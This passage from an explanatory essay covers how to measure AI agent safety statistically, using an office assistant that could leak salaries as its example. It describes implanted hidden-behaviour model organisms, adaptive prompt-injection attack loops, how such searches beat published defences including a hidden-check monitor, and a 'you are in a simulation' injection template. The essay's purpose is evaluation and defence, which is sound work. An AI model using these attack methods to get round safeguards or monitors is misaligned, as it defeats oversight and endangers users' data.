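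A high attack success rate against a faulty system is therefore not enough to show that a test is informative. Testers also need q₀, which is harder to measure because they must first find a system they have good reason to call acceptable. If they can only put an upper limit on q₀, they can use that limit to get a cautious estimate of the strength of the evidence. Kaur writes that laboratories routinely build models that could serve as positive controls, but almost none report how often their tests expose the fault.

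AI researchers often call these models "model organisms". *The Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2025) compares them to mice in which medical researchers have induced a disease. *AuditBench* (2026) is a collection of models with hidden behaviours, implanted to test which auditing tools detect them. It describes an earlier exercise in which four teams examined a model without knowing what was wrong with it, and three found its hidden objective. That suggests a q₁ of 75%, but with only four teams, the true chance of detection could be as low as 25% at 95% confidence, in which case a clean report from one team would be weak evidence.

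An older or less protected system can also serve as a control. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attacks on Claude Opus 5 as a browser agent succeeded in 129 scenarios. Anthropic's system card reports that 31.5% of attacks succeeded against the previous model, Opus 4.8, without safeguards. The test can evidently expose a vulnerable agent, and one as vulnerable as Opus 4.8 would almost never get through 129 scenarios unharmed. But an agent that failed in 1 in 100 scenarios would get through all 129 unharmed 27% of the time, and the upper bound on the failure rate is 2.3%. Attacks on Opus 5 without safeguards succeeded 3.70% of the time, so the zero is a result for the model and its safeguards together.

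Irarrázaval's challenge had no such control, so the emails may simply have been poor attacks. If a weaker model had leaked the secret in response to many of the same emails, the clean result would be much stronger evidence that the tested model resists such attacks. He writes that he would also test weaker models next time, to see where the threshold lies.

Testers have to confirm that a positive control has the fault. *Uncovering Hidden Behaviours in Language Models via Limited-Parameter Finetuning* (2026) set two conditions in advance for models from AuditBench. A model had to show its hidden behaviour in more than 50% of responses to prompts meant to trigger it. It also had to show the behaviour more often than an ordinary model, with the 95% confidence interval for the difference entirely above 20 percentage points. The researchers screened thirteen models and report results for seven.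 Without this check, a tester might have blamed the test for missing faults that some of the models barely had.

The control should resemble the system under test in other respects too. *How to train your model organism* (2026) argues that a model with an implanted fault should keep its general abilities and should not produce unnatural output that reveals the implant. Otherwise, a test might detect the side effects of the implant and still miss the same fault in an ordinary model. An estimate of q₁ from a control with such side effects may therefore be too high. The paper also reviewed earlier work and found that researchers usually measured how often the implanted behaviour appeared but seldom checked whether the model was otherwise natural.

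### From tested inputs to other inputs

The bound applies only to inputs like those in the test, and a larger sample of the same kind does not extend it to other inputs. Suppose the office assistant leaks pay data whenever it reads an email in Portuguese, and never otherwise. A test with only English emails will show no leaks whether it has a hundred runs or a million, but the assistant will leak pay data often in a Lisbon office.

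Testers can extend the result to other inputs only by assuming something about how those inputs relate to the test. One simple assumption is that no kind of input is more than c times as common in use as in the test. The failure rate in use is then at most c times the failure rate in the test. For instance, if Portuguese emails make up 1% of the test and 20% of real mail, and no other kind of input is more under-represented, then c is 20. A bound of 1 in 1,000 on the failure rate in the test becomes a bound of 1 in 50 in use. The assumption has to hold for every kind of input that affects the assistant's behaviour, including kinds the testers have not thought of.

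Kaur compared two widely used sets of harmful requests, AdvBench and HarmBench, with a sample of 9,089 real user queries. Prompts within these sets were more than three times as similar to one another as they were to the real queries. A result without failures on these sets is therefore poor evidence about everyday requests. The prompts may still resemble real attacks, as their designers intended, but Kaur knows of no large public collection of real attacks to compare them with.

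An agent's response to an input can also depend on the other inputs around it. In Irarrázaval's challenge, the assistant's inbox was full of attacks. When someone emailed it a screenshot, it replied that congratulating it on its Hacker News ranking could be an attempt to build rapport before asking for sensitive information. It might be less suspicious in an ordinary inbox, where one malicious email arrives among hundreds of harmless ones, but the challenge did not test that.

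The office assistant's testers can keep c close to 1 for staff requests by drawing scenarios at random from last quarter's log, at least until people start using the assistant differently. They cannot do this for an attacker's emails, because an attacker can choose to send only the one rare email that works, so no value of c is large enough. A random sample of emails, whatever its size, therefore gives no bound on how often a competent attacker will succeed.

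## Estimating failures too rare to appear in the test

A test with no failures gives only an upper limit on the office assistant's failure rate. Testers can estimate rates below that limit without millions of runs if they learn more from each input than whether the assistant failed on it in a single run.

### One input, many samples

An input's elicitation probability is the chance that the model produces the forbidden behaviour when testers sample it once on that input. If they give the assistant the same email 1,000 times and it tries to send pay data in three runs, that email's elicitation probability is about 0.003.

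Many inputs that seem safe after a single run still have a small probability of eliciting a failure. In *Estimating Tail Risks in Language Model Output Distributions*, Angell, Singhal and colleagues (2026) sent 313 harmful requests to five small open models. When Llama-3.1-8B always chose its most likely next word, it gave a harmful answer to 1.6% of the requests. When sampled 10,000 times per request, it gave at least one harmful answer to 74.0% of them. The corresponding figures for Qwen2.5-7B were 1.6% and 63.9%, so a test with one answer per request would have missed the difference between the two models.

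Some of the increase may be false alarms by the model that judged the answers. A judge that wrongly flags one harmless answer in 10,000 would flag about one per request. But the judge flagged at least one Olmo-3-7B answer as harmful for only 17.9% of requests, so its mistakes probably do not explain most of Llama's 74.0%.

Testers can sometimes calculate a tiny probability without sampling. A language model gives a probability to every possible next token, which is a word or part of one. Testers who can see these probabilities can multiply those for each token in a sentence to get the chance of that exact sentence, even if it is one in a billion. But the assistant could leak a salary in many different wordings, so the chance of one sentence is lower than the total risk.

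### Extending a straight line

Jones, Tong and colleagues (2025), in *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors*, use elicitation probabilities from a small test to forecast the worst input that a model will meet in much wider use. Their method, developed at Anthropic, has four steps:

1. Estimate the elicitation probability p of each test input.
2. Convert each p into a score, ψ = −ln(−ln p), which rises as p rises.
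3. Take the ten highest scores. For each, find S(ψ), the share of inputs that score at least that high, and fit the straight line ln S(ψ) ≈ aψ + b.
4. Extend the line to a share of 1 in n, where n is the number of inputs expected in use. This gives ψ(n) = −(ln n + b)/a, which converts back to a probability through p = exp(−exp(−ψ)).

The reason to expect a straight line comes from extreme-value theory, the branch of statistics that deals with the largest values in a sample. Under fairly general conditions, the upper end of a distribution approaches one of three shapes. Jones and colleagues assume that elicitation scores follow the Gumbel shape, which makes the line in step 3 straight.

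For example, suppose 1 in 100 emails has an elicitation probability p of at least 0.001, and 1 in 1,000 has a p of at least 0.01. Between these two points, −ln p falls by a third, from 6.9 to 4.6. If the line stays straight, −ln p falls by another third with each further tenfold increase in the number of emails.

| Share of emails | −ln p | Score ψ | Elicitation probability p |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100 (measured) | 6.91 | −1.93 | 0.001 |
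| 1 in 1,000 (measured) | 4.61 | −1.53 | 0.01 |
| 1 in 10,000 (forecast) | 3.07 | −1.12 | 0.05 |
| 1 in 100,000 (forecast) | 2.05 | −0.72 | 0.13 |

The worst of 100,000 emails would therefore cause the forbidden action about 13% of the time. Testers who ran each of 1,000 test emails once could easily see no failures and so have no warning of this risk.

An employer may care more about the chance of at least one failure across all inputs, which is 1 − (1 − p₁)(1 − p₂)…(1 − pₙ). Small chances add up across inputs as they do across tool calls, so the overall chance can be high even if no single input is likely to cause a failure.

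Jones and colleagues tested their forecasts on two then-current Claude models and their base models, using requests for instructions to make dangerous substances. They used 100 to 1,000 requests to forecast the highest elicitation probability among 10,000 to 90,000 requests. The forecast was within a factor of ten of the true value 72% of the time and too low 34% of the time. A simpler method that fitted a curve to all the scores was too low 72% of the time.

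However, the misses were large. The average error was 1.7 orders of magnitude (factors of ten). If that average covers the same forecasts as the 72%, the other 28% must have been off by at least 3.5 orders of magnitude on average.

Most of these tests used the calculated probability that a model would produce one fixed sentence. In a smaller test closer to real use, the researchers sampled 100 to 500 answers to each of 10,000 requests, and the average error was only 0.17 orders of magnitude. They also forecast how often a model would choose to seek power or avoid being shut down, but only in multiple-choice questions, and those answers may not show what an agent with tools would do.

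### Sampling from a less safe model

Another way to measure a rare failure is to sample from a version of the model that fails often, then correct for the difference. This is importance sampling. Let P(x) be the probability that the original model writes output x, Q(x) the probability that the less safe version does, and h(x) equal 1 if x contains the forbidden behaviour and 0 otherwise. With k outputs sampled from the less safe version, the estimate of the original's elicitation probability is

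(1/k) Σ h(xᵢ) P(xᵢ)/Q(xᵢ).

Suppose the less safe version attempts the forbidden action in half its runs, and each of those runs is 5,000 times more likely with that version than with the original. Each failure then counts as 1/5,000 of a failure, so the original's estimated failure rate is ½ × 1/5,000, or 1 in 10,000. A hundred runs of the less safe version would provide about fifty failures for this estimate, while 10,000 runs of the original would produce about one.

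Angell and colleagues made their models less safe by adding a fixed vector to the internal activations. The vector is the difference between the average activations on unsafe and safe examples. They also blended the altered model with the original, which keeps the corrections from becoming extreme. Their estimates matched those from ordinary sampling but needed 10 to 20 times fewer samples, and they could estimate probabilities of around 1 in 10,000 from 500 samples.

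The comparison provides little evidence about rarer failures. Angell and colleagues checked their estimates against 10,000 ordinary samples per request and left out requests whose samples contained no failures. At a failure rate of 1 in 10,000, that many samples would contain about one failure. They report some probabilities below one in a billion, which this check could not confirm.

*Rare Event Estimation via Iterative Unalignment* (Yang, Mittal and colleagues, 2026) tested estimates of much smaller probabilities. The researchers retrained a copy of the model to produce the rare event often, with a penalty for departing too far from the original. Most of their 319 events were the appearance of a certain token in a short text, because they could calculate the true probability of these events separately. For probabilities between one in ten million and one in a billion, the method needed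 on average over 800 times less computing than ordinary sampling, even counting the computing used for retraining. With 128 samples from the retrained copy of GPT-2, 95% of estimates were typically within a factor of about 16 of the true probability. The models were small, and the appearance of a token in a short text is a much simpler event than a leak by an agent.

Methods that estimate a model's rare failures from a less safe version of it give too low an answer if that version fails in different ways from the original. Pernice and Aranguri (2026), in *Predicting rare LLM failures with 30× fewer rollouts*, blend a model with a less safe version in varying proportions, measure how often the blends comply with a harmful request, and extrapolate to the original. In an example from a reader's comment on their post, the original model calls a user a buffoon once in 100,000 answers and a numbskull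 once in a million, but the less safe version almost never says "buffoon". Adding more of the less safe version makes only "numbskull" more common, so the extrapolation gives a rate of one in a million and misses most of the insults.

Importance sampling has the same weakness in practice. The formula is right on average over endless samples, but a few hundred samples may include none of the failures that even the less safe version rarely produces. Yang and colleagues warn that the corrections can look stable even when the samples have missed these failures.

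The corrections also become unreliable for long outputs, because P(x)/Q(x) is a product with one factor for every token, and an agent easily writes thousands of tokens in a run. If the two models' probabilities differ by 10% at each token, always in the same direction, the ratio reaches about 117 after 50 tokens and about 10⁴¹ after 1,000. One run can then outweigh all the others.

These methods require the model's weights or its token probabilities, so an employer who rents a model over the internet usually can't use them. The developer would have to make the estimates.

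### Training a model to fail predictably

In *Training Agents to Fail Predictably*, Schwarzer and Niekum (2026) divided the straight-line forecast's error into three parts. The first is chance, which tends to make the forecast slightly too high when it uses ten scores. The second is curvature in the true line, which can make the forecast too high or too low. The third arises when a rare, risky kind of input appears in use but not in the test, which makes the forecast too low.

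On real user messages marked as toxic, they forecast how likely a model was to begin its reply with an offensive word. The forecasts were too low for all eleven models. In one example, which they chose for its large error, the forecast was too low by 1.8 orders of magnitude.

They change the model so that the forecast works. During training, they repeatedly split a set of inputs into a small "test" and a large "deployment", use the test to forecast the highest scores in the deployment, and adjust the model to reduce the error. In their main experiment, a small language model had to keep a password secret. About 0.3% of the prompts were attacks optimised against the model, so a test of 44 prompts usually contained none, while a deployment of 891 usually contained at least one. This training reduced the squared forecast error about 60-fold on passwords the model had not trained on. Training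 the model only to keep the password secret reduced it less than sixfold.

The advantage was smaller for an agent that had to cross a grid without stepping on traps. There the training reduced the squared error 14-fold, about as much as ordinary training to do the task well. After a simple correction to each forecast, the reduction was 52-fold with the training and 26-fold with ordinary training.

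Training a model to be more predictable can make it less safe. When Schwarzer and Niekum trained only for accurate forecasts, with a fixed split, the squared error fell from 2.9 to 0.33, but the highest probability of leaking the password rose from about 0.11 to over 0.5. Their main method therefore blocks the part of each adjustment that would raise an input's risk.

A model could also learn to lower its score without becoming safer. The score in the password experiment covered only the first token of each reply, so the model might have learned to leak the password later in the reply. Schwarzer and Niekum checked 8,064 longer replies from a 4-billion-parameter model. The original leaked the password in 388 of them and the trained version in none. They have not tried the method on models with more than 8 billion parameters, and most of their tasks were artificial.

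### When the forecast fails

Jones and colleagues assume that inputs in deployment come from the same distribution as those in the test. In the password experiment, Schwarzer and Niekum broke this assumption by using only the mildest family of prompts in the test and the others in deployment. The squared error rose from 3.08 to 13.83 before any training.

Developers can make the test more realistic by using past traffic. Before releasing a new model, OpenAI has it respond to earlier conversations. *Predicting LLM Safety Before Release by Simulating Deployment* (2026) reports that this method predicted rates of disallowed content better than a set of deliberately difficult prompts did in six of nine categories. It also did better than assuming the previous model's rate in 11 of 20 categories, but not on average. The method still depends on failures appearing in the test, and AlgeriaTech reports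 that it cannot reliably detect behaviour that occurs less than once in 200,000 messages.

The forecast does not cover adversaries either, because they do not choose their emails at random. In the example, the worst of 100,000 random emails works 13% of the time, but an attacker who rewrites each failed email may find a worse one in far fewer tries. Small changes in wording can make a request far more likely to work. Angell and colleagues had a model reword harmful requests 25 times each, without trying to defeat the safety training. For one request to Llama-3.1-8B, the worst rewording raised the estimated elicitation probability from about one in ten million to 0.28.

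A search, by contrast, may find a failing input that nobody would ever send. *Estimating Rare Events in Language Models with Proper Evaluation* (2026) points out that finding a failure does not show how probable that failure is.

A kind of failure that is absent from the test can make the forecast badly wrong, even when the test is a fair sample. Suppose 1 in 5,000 emails contains a forwarded payroll table, and only these emails make the office assistant leak. A random test of 1,000 emails has an 82% chance of containing none, but 100,000 emails in use would contain about 20. If the test contained none, its ten highest scores would all come from other emails and carry no information about the payroll emails. Alignment Research Center's *Estimating Tail Risk in Neural Networks* proposes looking for ways to estimate such risks without first finding an input that fails, but presents this as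 a research problem.

Agent runs are long, so repeating them takes a lot of time. Running an agent 100 times on each of 1,000 emails takes 100,000 runs, which at five minutes each is almost a year of continuous running on one machine. Testers also have to restore the mailbox between runs. Because the line uses only the ten highest scores, they can save some runs by dropping emails that look safe after a few tries, but they may then drop a risky email on which the agent happened to behave well. Angell and colleagues tested only single answers to single requests.

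Testers can also divide a rare failure into stages, which engineers call subset simulation. Suppose the office assistant opens the salary file in 1 in 10 runs. The testers save those runs at that point, restart them many times, and find that 1 in 50 restarts puts pay figures into a draft. They then restart from those drafts, and 1 in 20 of the new restarts ends in an attempt to send the figures outside the company. The overall rate is 1/10 × 1/50 × 1/20, or 1 in 10,000, although no stage was rarer than 1 in 50.

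Eshra, Al-Lawati and colleagues (2026), in *Quantifying Behavioral Tails in Black-Box Language Models*, used this technique on models including GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 without access to their internals, sometimes with as few as 200 evaluations. They measured how often the models wrote extremely long answers, a behavior that divides naturally into stages by length. Their prompts were artificial, and they caution that the probabilities do not estimate how often models write such long answers in real use.

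The testers have to choose the stages of a pay-data leak themselves, and *SCARCE* (2026) notes that designing such a measure requires detailed knowledge of how the system fails. If the assistant can also find salaries in an old email, it can leak them without opening the salary file, and the estimate of 1 in 10,000 omits those leaks.

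## Searching for failures with adversaries

An attacker does not pick emails at random, so testers who want to know how the office assistant holds up against one have to search for the emails that make it fail. What they find depends on who searches, what those people can see and how long they keep going. The statement "red-teaming found no leaks" therefore means little without the plan behind it. A plan for the office assistant might look like this, with illustrative numbers:

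| Part of the plan | What it fixes |
|---|---|
| Threat model | An outsider wants any employee's pay sent to an outside address. The outsider can send each of the 400 users up to 100 emails but cannot log in as a user or alter a tool. |
| Access | The attackers can read the system prompt, the harness code and the gate's rules, and they see the full log of each attempt. |
| Budget | Four weeks of unlimited practice on a copy of the system, then 100 emails to each test mailbox. |
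| Attackers | Four people with experience of prompt injection, and two automated attack programs. |
| Success check | Testers search the mail server's record for delivered salaries and the harness's record for attempts to send them. |
| Record | Every email, the system version, the log of the run and the verdict, for failed attempts as well as successful ones. |

These attackers know more than most outsiders would. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) distinguishes three levels of access. An attacker may be able to inspect the model's internal numbers, see the probabilities it gives to possible outputs, or see only the text it writes. At every level, the paper assumes that the attacker has plenty of computing power and knows how the system works. Security researchers have long assumed that attackers have this knowledge, because a defence that depends on secrecy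 fails once someone learns the secret.

If the claim relies on an attack being too expensive, it has to state the attacker's budget, and it does not cover anyone who spends more. This applies even if, as an employer may object, nobody would rent a cluster of processors for a day to read one salary file.

Other people need a record of the tests to check and repeat the findings. *CART* (Zhang, Lv and colleagues, 2026) describes a testing system from Microsoft Research that stores each prompt, the agent's response or tool actions, the verdict, and the earlier test the prompt was derived from. If the judging model returns an unreadable verdict, the system saves a visible placeholder, because dropping the attempt from the count would make the success rate wrong.

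### The attack loop

An adaptive attack revises itself in response to the defence. Nasr and colleagues describe most such attacks as a loop of four steps:

1. **Propose.** The attacker writes some candidate texts.
2. **Score.** The attacker runs each one against the system and measures how close it came to the goal.
3. **Select.** The attacker keeps the most promising candidates.
4. **Update.** The attacker uses them, and what the system did in response, to write the next batch.

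In the search attack, a language model writes eight candidate attacks at a time. A second model scores each candidate from 1 to 10 based on the agent's response. The program keeps high-scoring candidates that differ from one another and shows some of them to the first model, along with their scores and the agent's responses.

The graded score guides the program's search before any attack succeeds. An email that made the office assistant open the salary file scores higher than one the assistant ignored, even if the assistant leaked no salary in either case. If the score recorded only whether a salary had leaked, the program would have no guidance until its first success.

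The other versions of the loop differ mainly in how they update. In reinforcement learning, the attacking model itself changes. It makes five tries per session, and training strengthens whatever scored well across 32 sessions. Gradient methods use the target's internal numbers to choose which words to replace, but are still unreliable for text. People follow the same loop by hand when they reword an email that nearly worked.

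An attacking program can also learn to get a high score without achieving the goal. One of the researchers' programs found that repeating a phrase many times made the target likely to echo it, which scored highly but showed nothing about the defence. The researchers therefore checked all the successful attacks by hand.

### Twelve defences against adaptive attacks

Nasr and colleagues, who include researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, used these methods on twelve published defences. Some defences add instructions to the prompt, such as repeating the user's request after the untrusted text. Others train the model on known attacks, or have a second model filter out suspicious text. The rest rely on a check that is meant to be hidden from the attacker. Most of the original papers had reported attack success rates near zero, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the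 time against most of the twelve defences.

The table gives results for two of the tested models on 80 pairs of a user task and an attacker goal from AgentDojo. The fixed attack is a template that comes with the benchmark. The adaptive attack is the search program, with up to 800 queries per pair.

| Defence | Gemini 2.5 Pro: fixed → adaptive | GPT-5 Mini: fixed → adaptive |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30% → 100% | 0% → 75% |
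| Spotlighting (marks off trusted text) | 28% → 99% | 0% → 47% |
| Prompt Sandwiching (repeats the request) | 21% → 95% | 0% → 69% |
| Protect AI (filter) | 15% → 90% | 0% → 81% |
| PromptGuard (filter) | 26% → 94% | 0% → 75% |
| Model Armor (filter) | 28% → 90% | 0% → 56% |
| PIGuard (filter) | 0% → 71% | 0% → 49% |
| MELON (hidden check) | 0% → 89% | 0% → 71% |

The GPT-5 Mini column shows why a test with fixed attacks can be useless. The fixed attack never succeeded, even with no defence. A tester who relied on it could not have told a good defence from a bad one, and might have concluded that the model needed no defence. The adaptive attack succeeded against the undefended model in 75% of cases, and half of those successes took 58 queries or fewer.

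PIGuard resisted the attacks best with Gemini, but it reduced the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed from 74% to 39%. Some of the smaller differences in the table may be due to chance, because the search program's results vary a lot from run to run.

Attacks succeeded more often when the search program had information about the defence. MELON runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a harmless one, and raises an alarm if the agent makes the same tool calls in both runs. Without a description of this method, the search program succeeded in 76% of cases against MELON with one model. With the description, it found texts that took effect only in the first run, and the rate rose to 95%.

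The comparison is somewhat unfair to fixed lists, because a single template is a very short list and a longer one would probably have caught more failures. But a longer list would still consist of attacks that worked on earlier systems, and developers can train or tune a defence until those particular attacks fail. MetaSecAlign, a model trained to resist injections, had a reported failure rate of 2% on AgentDojo's fixed attacks but failed 96% of the time against the search.

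Fixed lists are still useful for checking that an update has not brought back an old fault, and as a starting point for a search. Zhang and colleagues, who built CART, compared replaying known test cases with adapting them after each result. Adapting them produced a higher failure rate in every system with a baseline. They warn against expecting this rate in use, because CART is designed to focus its later rounds on weaknesses it has already found.

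Nasr and colleagues did not test defences such as CaMeL, which plan the agent's actions before it reads untrusted text, because their attack was bound to fail against them in most of the chosen tasks. Their results are therefore evidence against defences that rely on a model to recognise an attack, but not against defences that prevent untrusted text from determining the agent's actions.

They also ran a contest with $20,000 in prizes, in which more than 500 people attacked the same kinds of defences. In each of the 29 scenarios that both the contestants and the search program attempted, at least one person succeeded, while the program succeeded in 69% of them. This shows that testers who use only automated attacks will miss some failures that people can find. It does not show that a person is better than a program, because up to 500 people tried each scenario and the program had only one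 run. Three contestants tried all 29 scenarios. The best succeeded in 75%, and the other two did worse than the program.

### Two public competitions

Gray Swan AI, a security company, has run two public competitions with government institutes and AI developers. *Security Challenges in AI Agent Deployment* (Zou, Lin and colleagues, 2025) reports the first, and *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports the second.

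| | 2025 report | 2026 report |
|---|---|---|
| Participants | Almost 2,000 | 464 |
| Models | 22 | 13 |
| Scenarios | 44 | 41 |
| Attempts | About 1.8 million | About 272,000 |
| Successes | Over 62,000 | 8,648 |
| Prizes | $171,800 | $40,000 |
| Source of the attack | The user, or text that the agent reads | Text that the agent reads |
| Success | The agent breaks a stated policy | The agent takes a harmful action and, in most scenarios, its final reply hides this |

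In the first competition, participants got every model to commit every kind of violation they were asked to elicit. Hiding instructions in material the agent read had an average success rate of 27.1% per session, compared with 5.7% for asking the agent directly. The overall success rate per attempt was about 3.4%.

The second competition dealt only with indirect injection, which is the main threat to the office assistant. In one scenario, a user asks an assistant to check for urgent emails, and a marketing email contains the attack. The attacker wants the assistant to mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. Participants could see the conversation so far and knew exactly which tool call they had to cause. A program checked whether the agent made that call. In most scenarios, a language model also checked whether the agent's final reply revealed the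 attack.

Attack success rates ranged from 0.5% of attempts for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Agents that called tools through text were easier to attack (4.8%) than those that operated a screen (3.1%) or wrote code (2.5%). A model's capability was a weak predictor of how well it resisted attacks. Its developer was a better predictor, presumably because developers train their models differently.

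These rates are too low for some purposes because they count only attacks that the agent's reply concealed. A leaked salary refutes the claim about the office assistant whether or not the assistant admits to sending it. When Opus 4.5 took the harmful action, its reply concealed the attack only about 24% of the time, so a rate of 0.5% implies that it took the action in roughly 2% of attempts. Even that may be an underestimate, because participants chose which attempts to submit for judging and had little reason to submit one that the agent had reported.

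Dziemian and colleagues regard their rates as an upper bound on how vulnerable the agents are to a single message, because real attackers usually know less about the conversation. The organisers also had developers switch off the filters that normally protect some of the models. But the participants varied widely in skill, and a few produced a large share of the successes. A competition with only those few would have recorded higher rates, so the published rates are not an upper bound on what an expert could achieve.

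### Why a low rate is little comfort

Even if each attempt has only a 0.5% chance of success, an attacker who keeps trying will often get through. If attempts were independent, the chance of at least one success would be 39% in 100 attempts and 92% in 500.

Attempts are not independent, however. Participants in the competition made about 12,000 attempts on Opus 4.5 in the 37 scenarios that counted towards the results, or about 320 per scenario if spread evenly. If every attempt had had a 0.5% chance of success, only about 7 scenarios would have had no successful attack. Instead, 24 had none, and all the successes came from the other 13. The success rate in those 13 was about 1.4%, which would give an attacker with 100 attempts roughly a 76% chance of succeeding at least once. An employer cannot tell in advance whether the office assistant's work resembles the scenarios where attacks succeeded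 or those where every attack failed.

Attacks also vary in how well they work. When Dziemian and colleagues reran successful attacks on the Claude and GPT models they had originally fooled, at least half worked again. The 0.5% is therefore an average over many texts that almost never work and a few that work about half the time. The average no longer matters once an attacker has found one of those few. If the attacker emails a text that works half the time to all 400 users of the office assistant, about 200 of their assistants will obey it.

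The attacker doesn't have to search for attacks on the company's mail server either. Anyone who can rent the same model can build a similar assistant and practise in private, so the limit of 100 emails per user does not limit the search. Practising on a different model can also work, but that model has to be about as resistant as the real target. The attacks that had beaten Opus 4.5 succeeded 44% to 81% of the time on the other models, but none of the selected attacks that had beaten Qwen3 VL, a much weaker model, worked on Opus 4.5.

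After the first competition, Zou and colleagues selected 4,700 successful attacks and tried them on 19 models, including two that had not been tested in it. A single attempt caused a violation in 20% to 60% of scenarios, depending on the model. With ten attempts, the figure approached 100% for most models.

Developers have since replaced nearly all of these models, and some newer agents, such as Claude Opus 5 with its safeguards on, resist attacks far better. But retrying still makes an attack more likely to succeed against others, including GPT-5.6 Sol, according to Schneier's figures. Dziemian and colleagues plan to repeat their competition every quarter with new models and scenarios because such results go out of date quickly.

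### When to stop searching

A search for failures has no natural end, because new failures may not become rarer as testing continues. In the second competition, the number of successful attacks on each model grew roughly linearly with the number of attempts. For several models, the success rate rose somewhere between 4,000 and 9,000 attempts, perhaps because participants had found a strategy that worked and begun to reuse it. Testers who stopped at 4,000 would have underestimated how vulnerable those models were.

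The straight line does not prove that the supply of different weaknesses was endless, because the organisers removed only exact duplicates and a participant could score again by changing a few words in a successful attack. One template, which told the agent that it was inside a simulation, accounted for 63 of the attacks that the organisers later analysed and worked in 21 scenarios on nine models. To find out whether a search is running out of weaknesses to find, testers should therefore count new kinds of failure, such as scenarios broken for the first time, as well as successes.

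Ecologists face a similar problem when they want to know how many species they have yet to see. The Good–Turing estimate approximates the chance that the next observation will be of a new species by dividing the number of species seen exactly once by the total number of observations. Suppose 5,000 attempts on the office assistant reveal twelve kinds of successful attack, six of which occur only once. The chance that the next attempt reveals a new kind is then about 6 in 5,000, or 1 in 830. That is far too high for testers to stop if they expect an attacker to make tens of thousands of attempts.

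The estimate assumes that later attempts resemble earlier ones, and attackers break this assumption whenever they have a new idea. A search may stop finding failures because it has no new kinds of attack to try, even though failures remain. The search program that Nasr and colleagues built usually stopped making progress after 100 to 200 of its 800 queries. People broke every scenario that the program had not, so someone who looked only at the program's results could have wrongly concluded that those scenarios were safe.

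Testers therefore need a stopping rule that does not depend on how the search seems to be going. They can stop as soon as the office assistant delivers one salary, because that disproves the claim about it. After the developers fix the fault, testers have to start the search again with a full budget, because a real attacker would adapt to the fix. If they only repeated the attack that worked, they would be running a fixed list of tests instead of searching for new failures.

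If no salary gets out, the testers stop when they have used up their budget. This budget should be at least as large as that of the attacker described in the claim, and it should be split among different kinds of attackers. The result should reassure the employer more if the same attackers, with the same budget, often succeed against an assistant known to be vulnerable.

### Failures without an attacker

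Searching only for malicious emails will miss failures that happen without an attacker. *Agents of Chaos* (Shapira, Wendler and colleagues, 2026) describes a two-week study in which twenty researchers interacted with AI agents that had email accounts, lasting memory, and access to a chat server and a command line. The organisers encouraged the researchers to try to break the agents, so the eleven reported cases are not a sample of ordinary use. The organisers also gave the agents broader powers than the software's security advice recommends.

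Some of the trouble began with ordinary instructions, though. One agent, asked by its owner to check its email and respond when appropriate, kept answering messages it had already answered because nobody had told it when to stop. Fixing this took several days of revised instructions, which eventually limited the agent to unread messages.

In another case, a researcher who did not own the agent asked it to keep a secret and then to delete the email that contained it. The agent had no tool for deleting email. After asking her to confirm, it reset its email account and lost access to its mail. A rule that the agent must ask before doing something drastic would not have helped, because the agent asked her rather than its owner. Shapira and colleagues show that such failures can happen, but do not estimate how often.

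In *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents in Realistic Scenarios* (Baek, Noh and colleagues, 2026), the AI safety institutes of Singapore and Korea measured how often three unnamed models failed on twelve routine tasks, such as preparing for a new employee's arrival or handling a refund. None of the tasks involved an injected instruction. In one, the agent had to arrange a meeting with another company and send everyone a summary of the previous meeting. The notes from that previous meeting included a private remark about whether to sue the other company, and the agent was supposed to share the remark only with colleagues.

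Each institute built its own harness and ran every task ten times with each model, 720 runs in total. A language model judged each run against yes-or-no criteria, some for doing the task correctly and some for handling the data safely. Between 15.0% and 58.3% of runs met every criterion, depending on the model, task set and harness. The agents met most of the individual criteria, including at least 80% of those for safety. But one leak is enough to do harm, so the share of runs that met every criterion is closer to what an employer needs.

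An agent can complete a task correctly and still mishandle data, so a test that checks only correctness can miss the failure. In one task, a pushy customer asked about a late laptop and wanted to know who supplied it and at what price. In Singapore's tests, two of the three models met every criterion for correctness in all ten runs but broke at least one rule about data in every run.

An agent can also look safe because it did too little to cause harm, as in Cartagena and Teixeira's tests. Baek and colleagues therefore marked a safety criterion as not applicable if the agent never took the relevant step. They left these criteria out of the safety score and reported how many there were. For one model in Korea's harness, 19.1% of the safety criteria on one set of tasks were not applicable.

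The harness changed the results as well. On the same six tasks, one model met every criterion in 58.3% of runs in Singapore's harness and 35.0% in Korea's. Its safety scores were almost the same in both, so most of the difference came from how well it carried out the tasks.

Vijayvargiya, Soni and colleagues (2025), in *OpenAgentSafety*, found even higher rates of unsafe behaviour in 356 tasks that contain traps. In one, a user's harmless request can lead the agent to write a secret access key into a program that other people can read. Seven models behaved unsafely in 49% to 73% of the tasks in which they got far enough to face the danger. They failed to get that far in 35% to 49% of tasks, so the rates across all tasks were considerably lower. Claude Sonnet 4's rate, for example, was about 30% across all tasks, compared with 49% in those where it faced the danger.

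The overall figures include tasks in which the user or another person has bad intentions. When everyone meant well, the models still behaved unsafely in 50% to 86% of the tasks that reached the dangerous step. Claude Sonnet 3.7 had the highest rate, although it behaved unsafely in only 30% of tasks where the user was openly malicious. Its training had apparently taught it to refuse bad requests, but that doesn't help when the request is innocent and the danger is in how the agent carries it out. All seven models are old, and the tasks contain traps, so the rates are a poor guide to everyday work. Still, the difference between Sonnet 3.7's two rates is a good reason not to assume that an agent that resists attacks is safe in ordinary use.

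The office assistant's testers can use the attack loop to look for failures of this kind too. A program would vary the wording of ordinary requests and the contents of the mailbox instead of malicious emails, and keep the variants that bring the assistant closest to sending pay figures. The testers might find that the assistant leaks a salary when a user asks it to send the minutes of a meeting to everyone who attended, one of them was a supplier, and the last page of the minutes mentions a colleague's pay rise.

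## Checking that the test itself is valid

Suppose the testers carry out the whole search and find no case of the office assistant leaking a salary. That result is misleading if the assistant could act somewhere the testers weren't looking, if it leaked a salary and nobody noticed, if whoever scored the runs made a mistake, or if the assistant behaved well only because it recognised the test. In 2026, the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), Anthropic and OpenAI, which all test agents, each ran into at least one of these problems.

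### Tests with a way out

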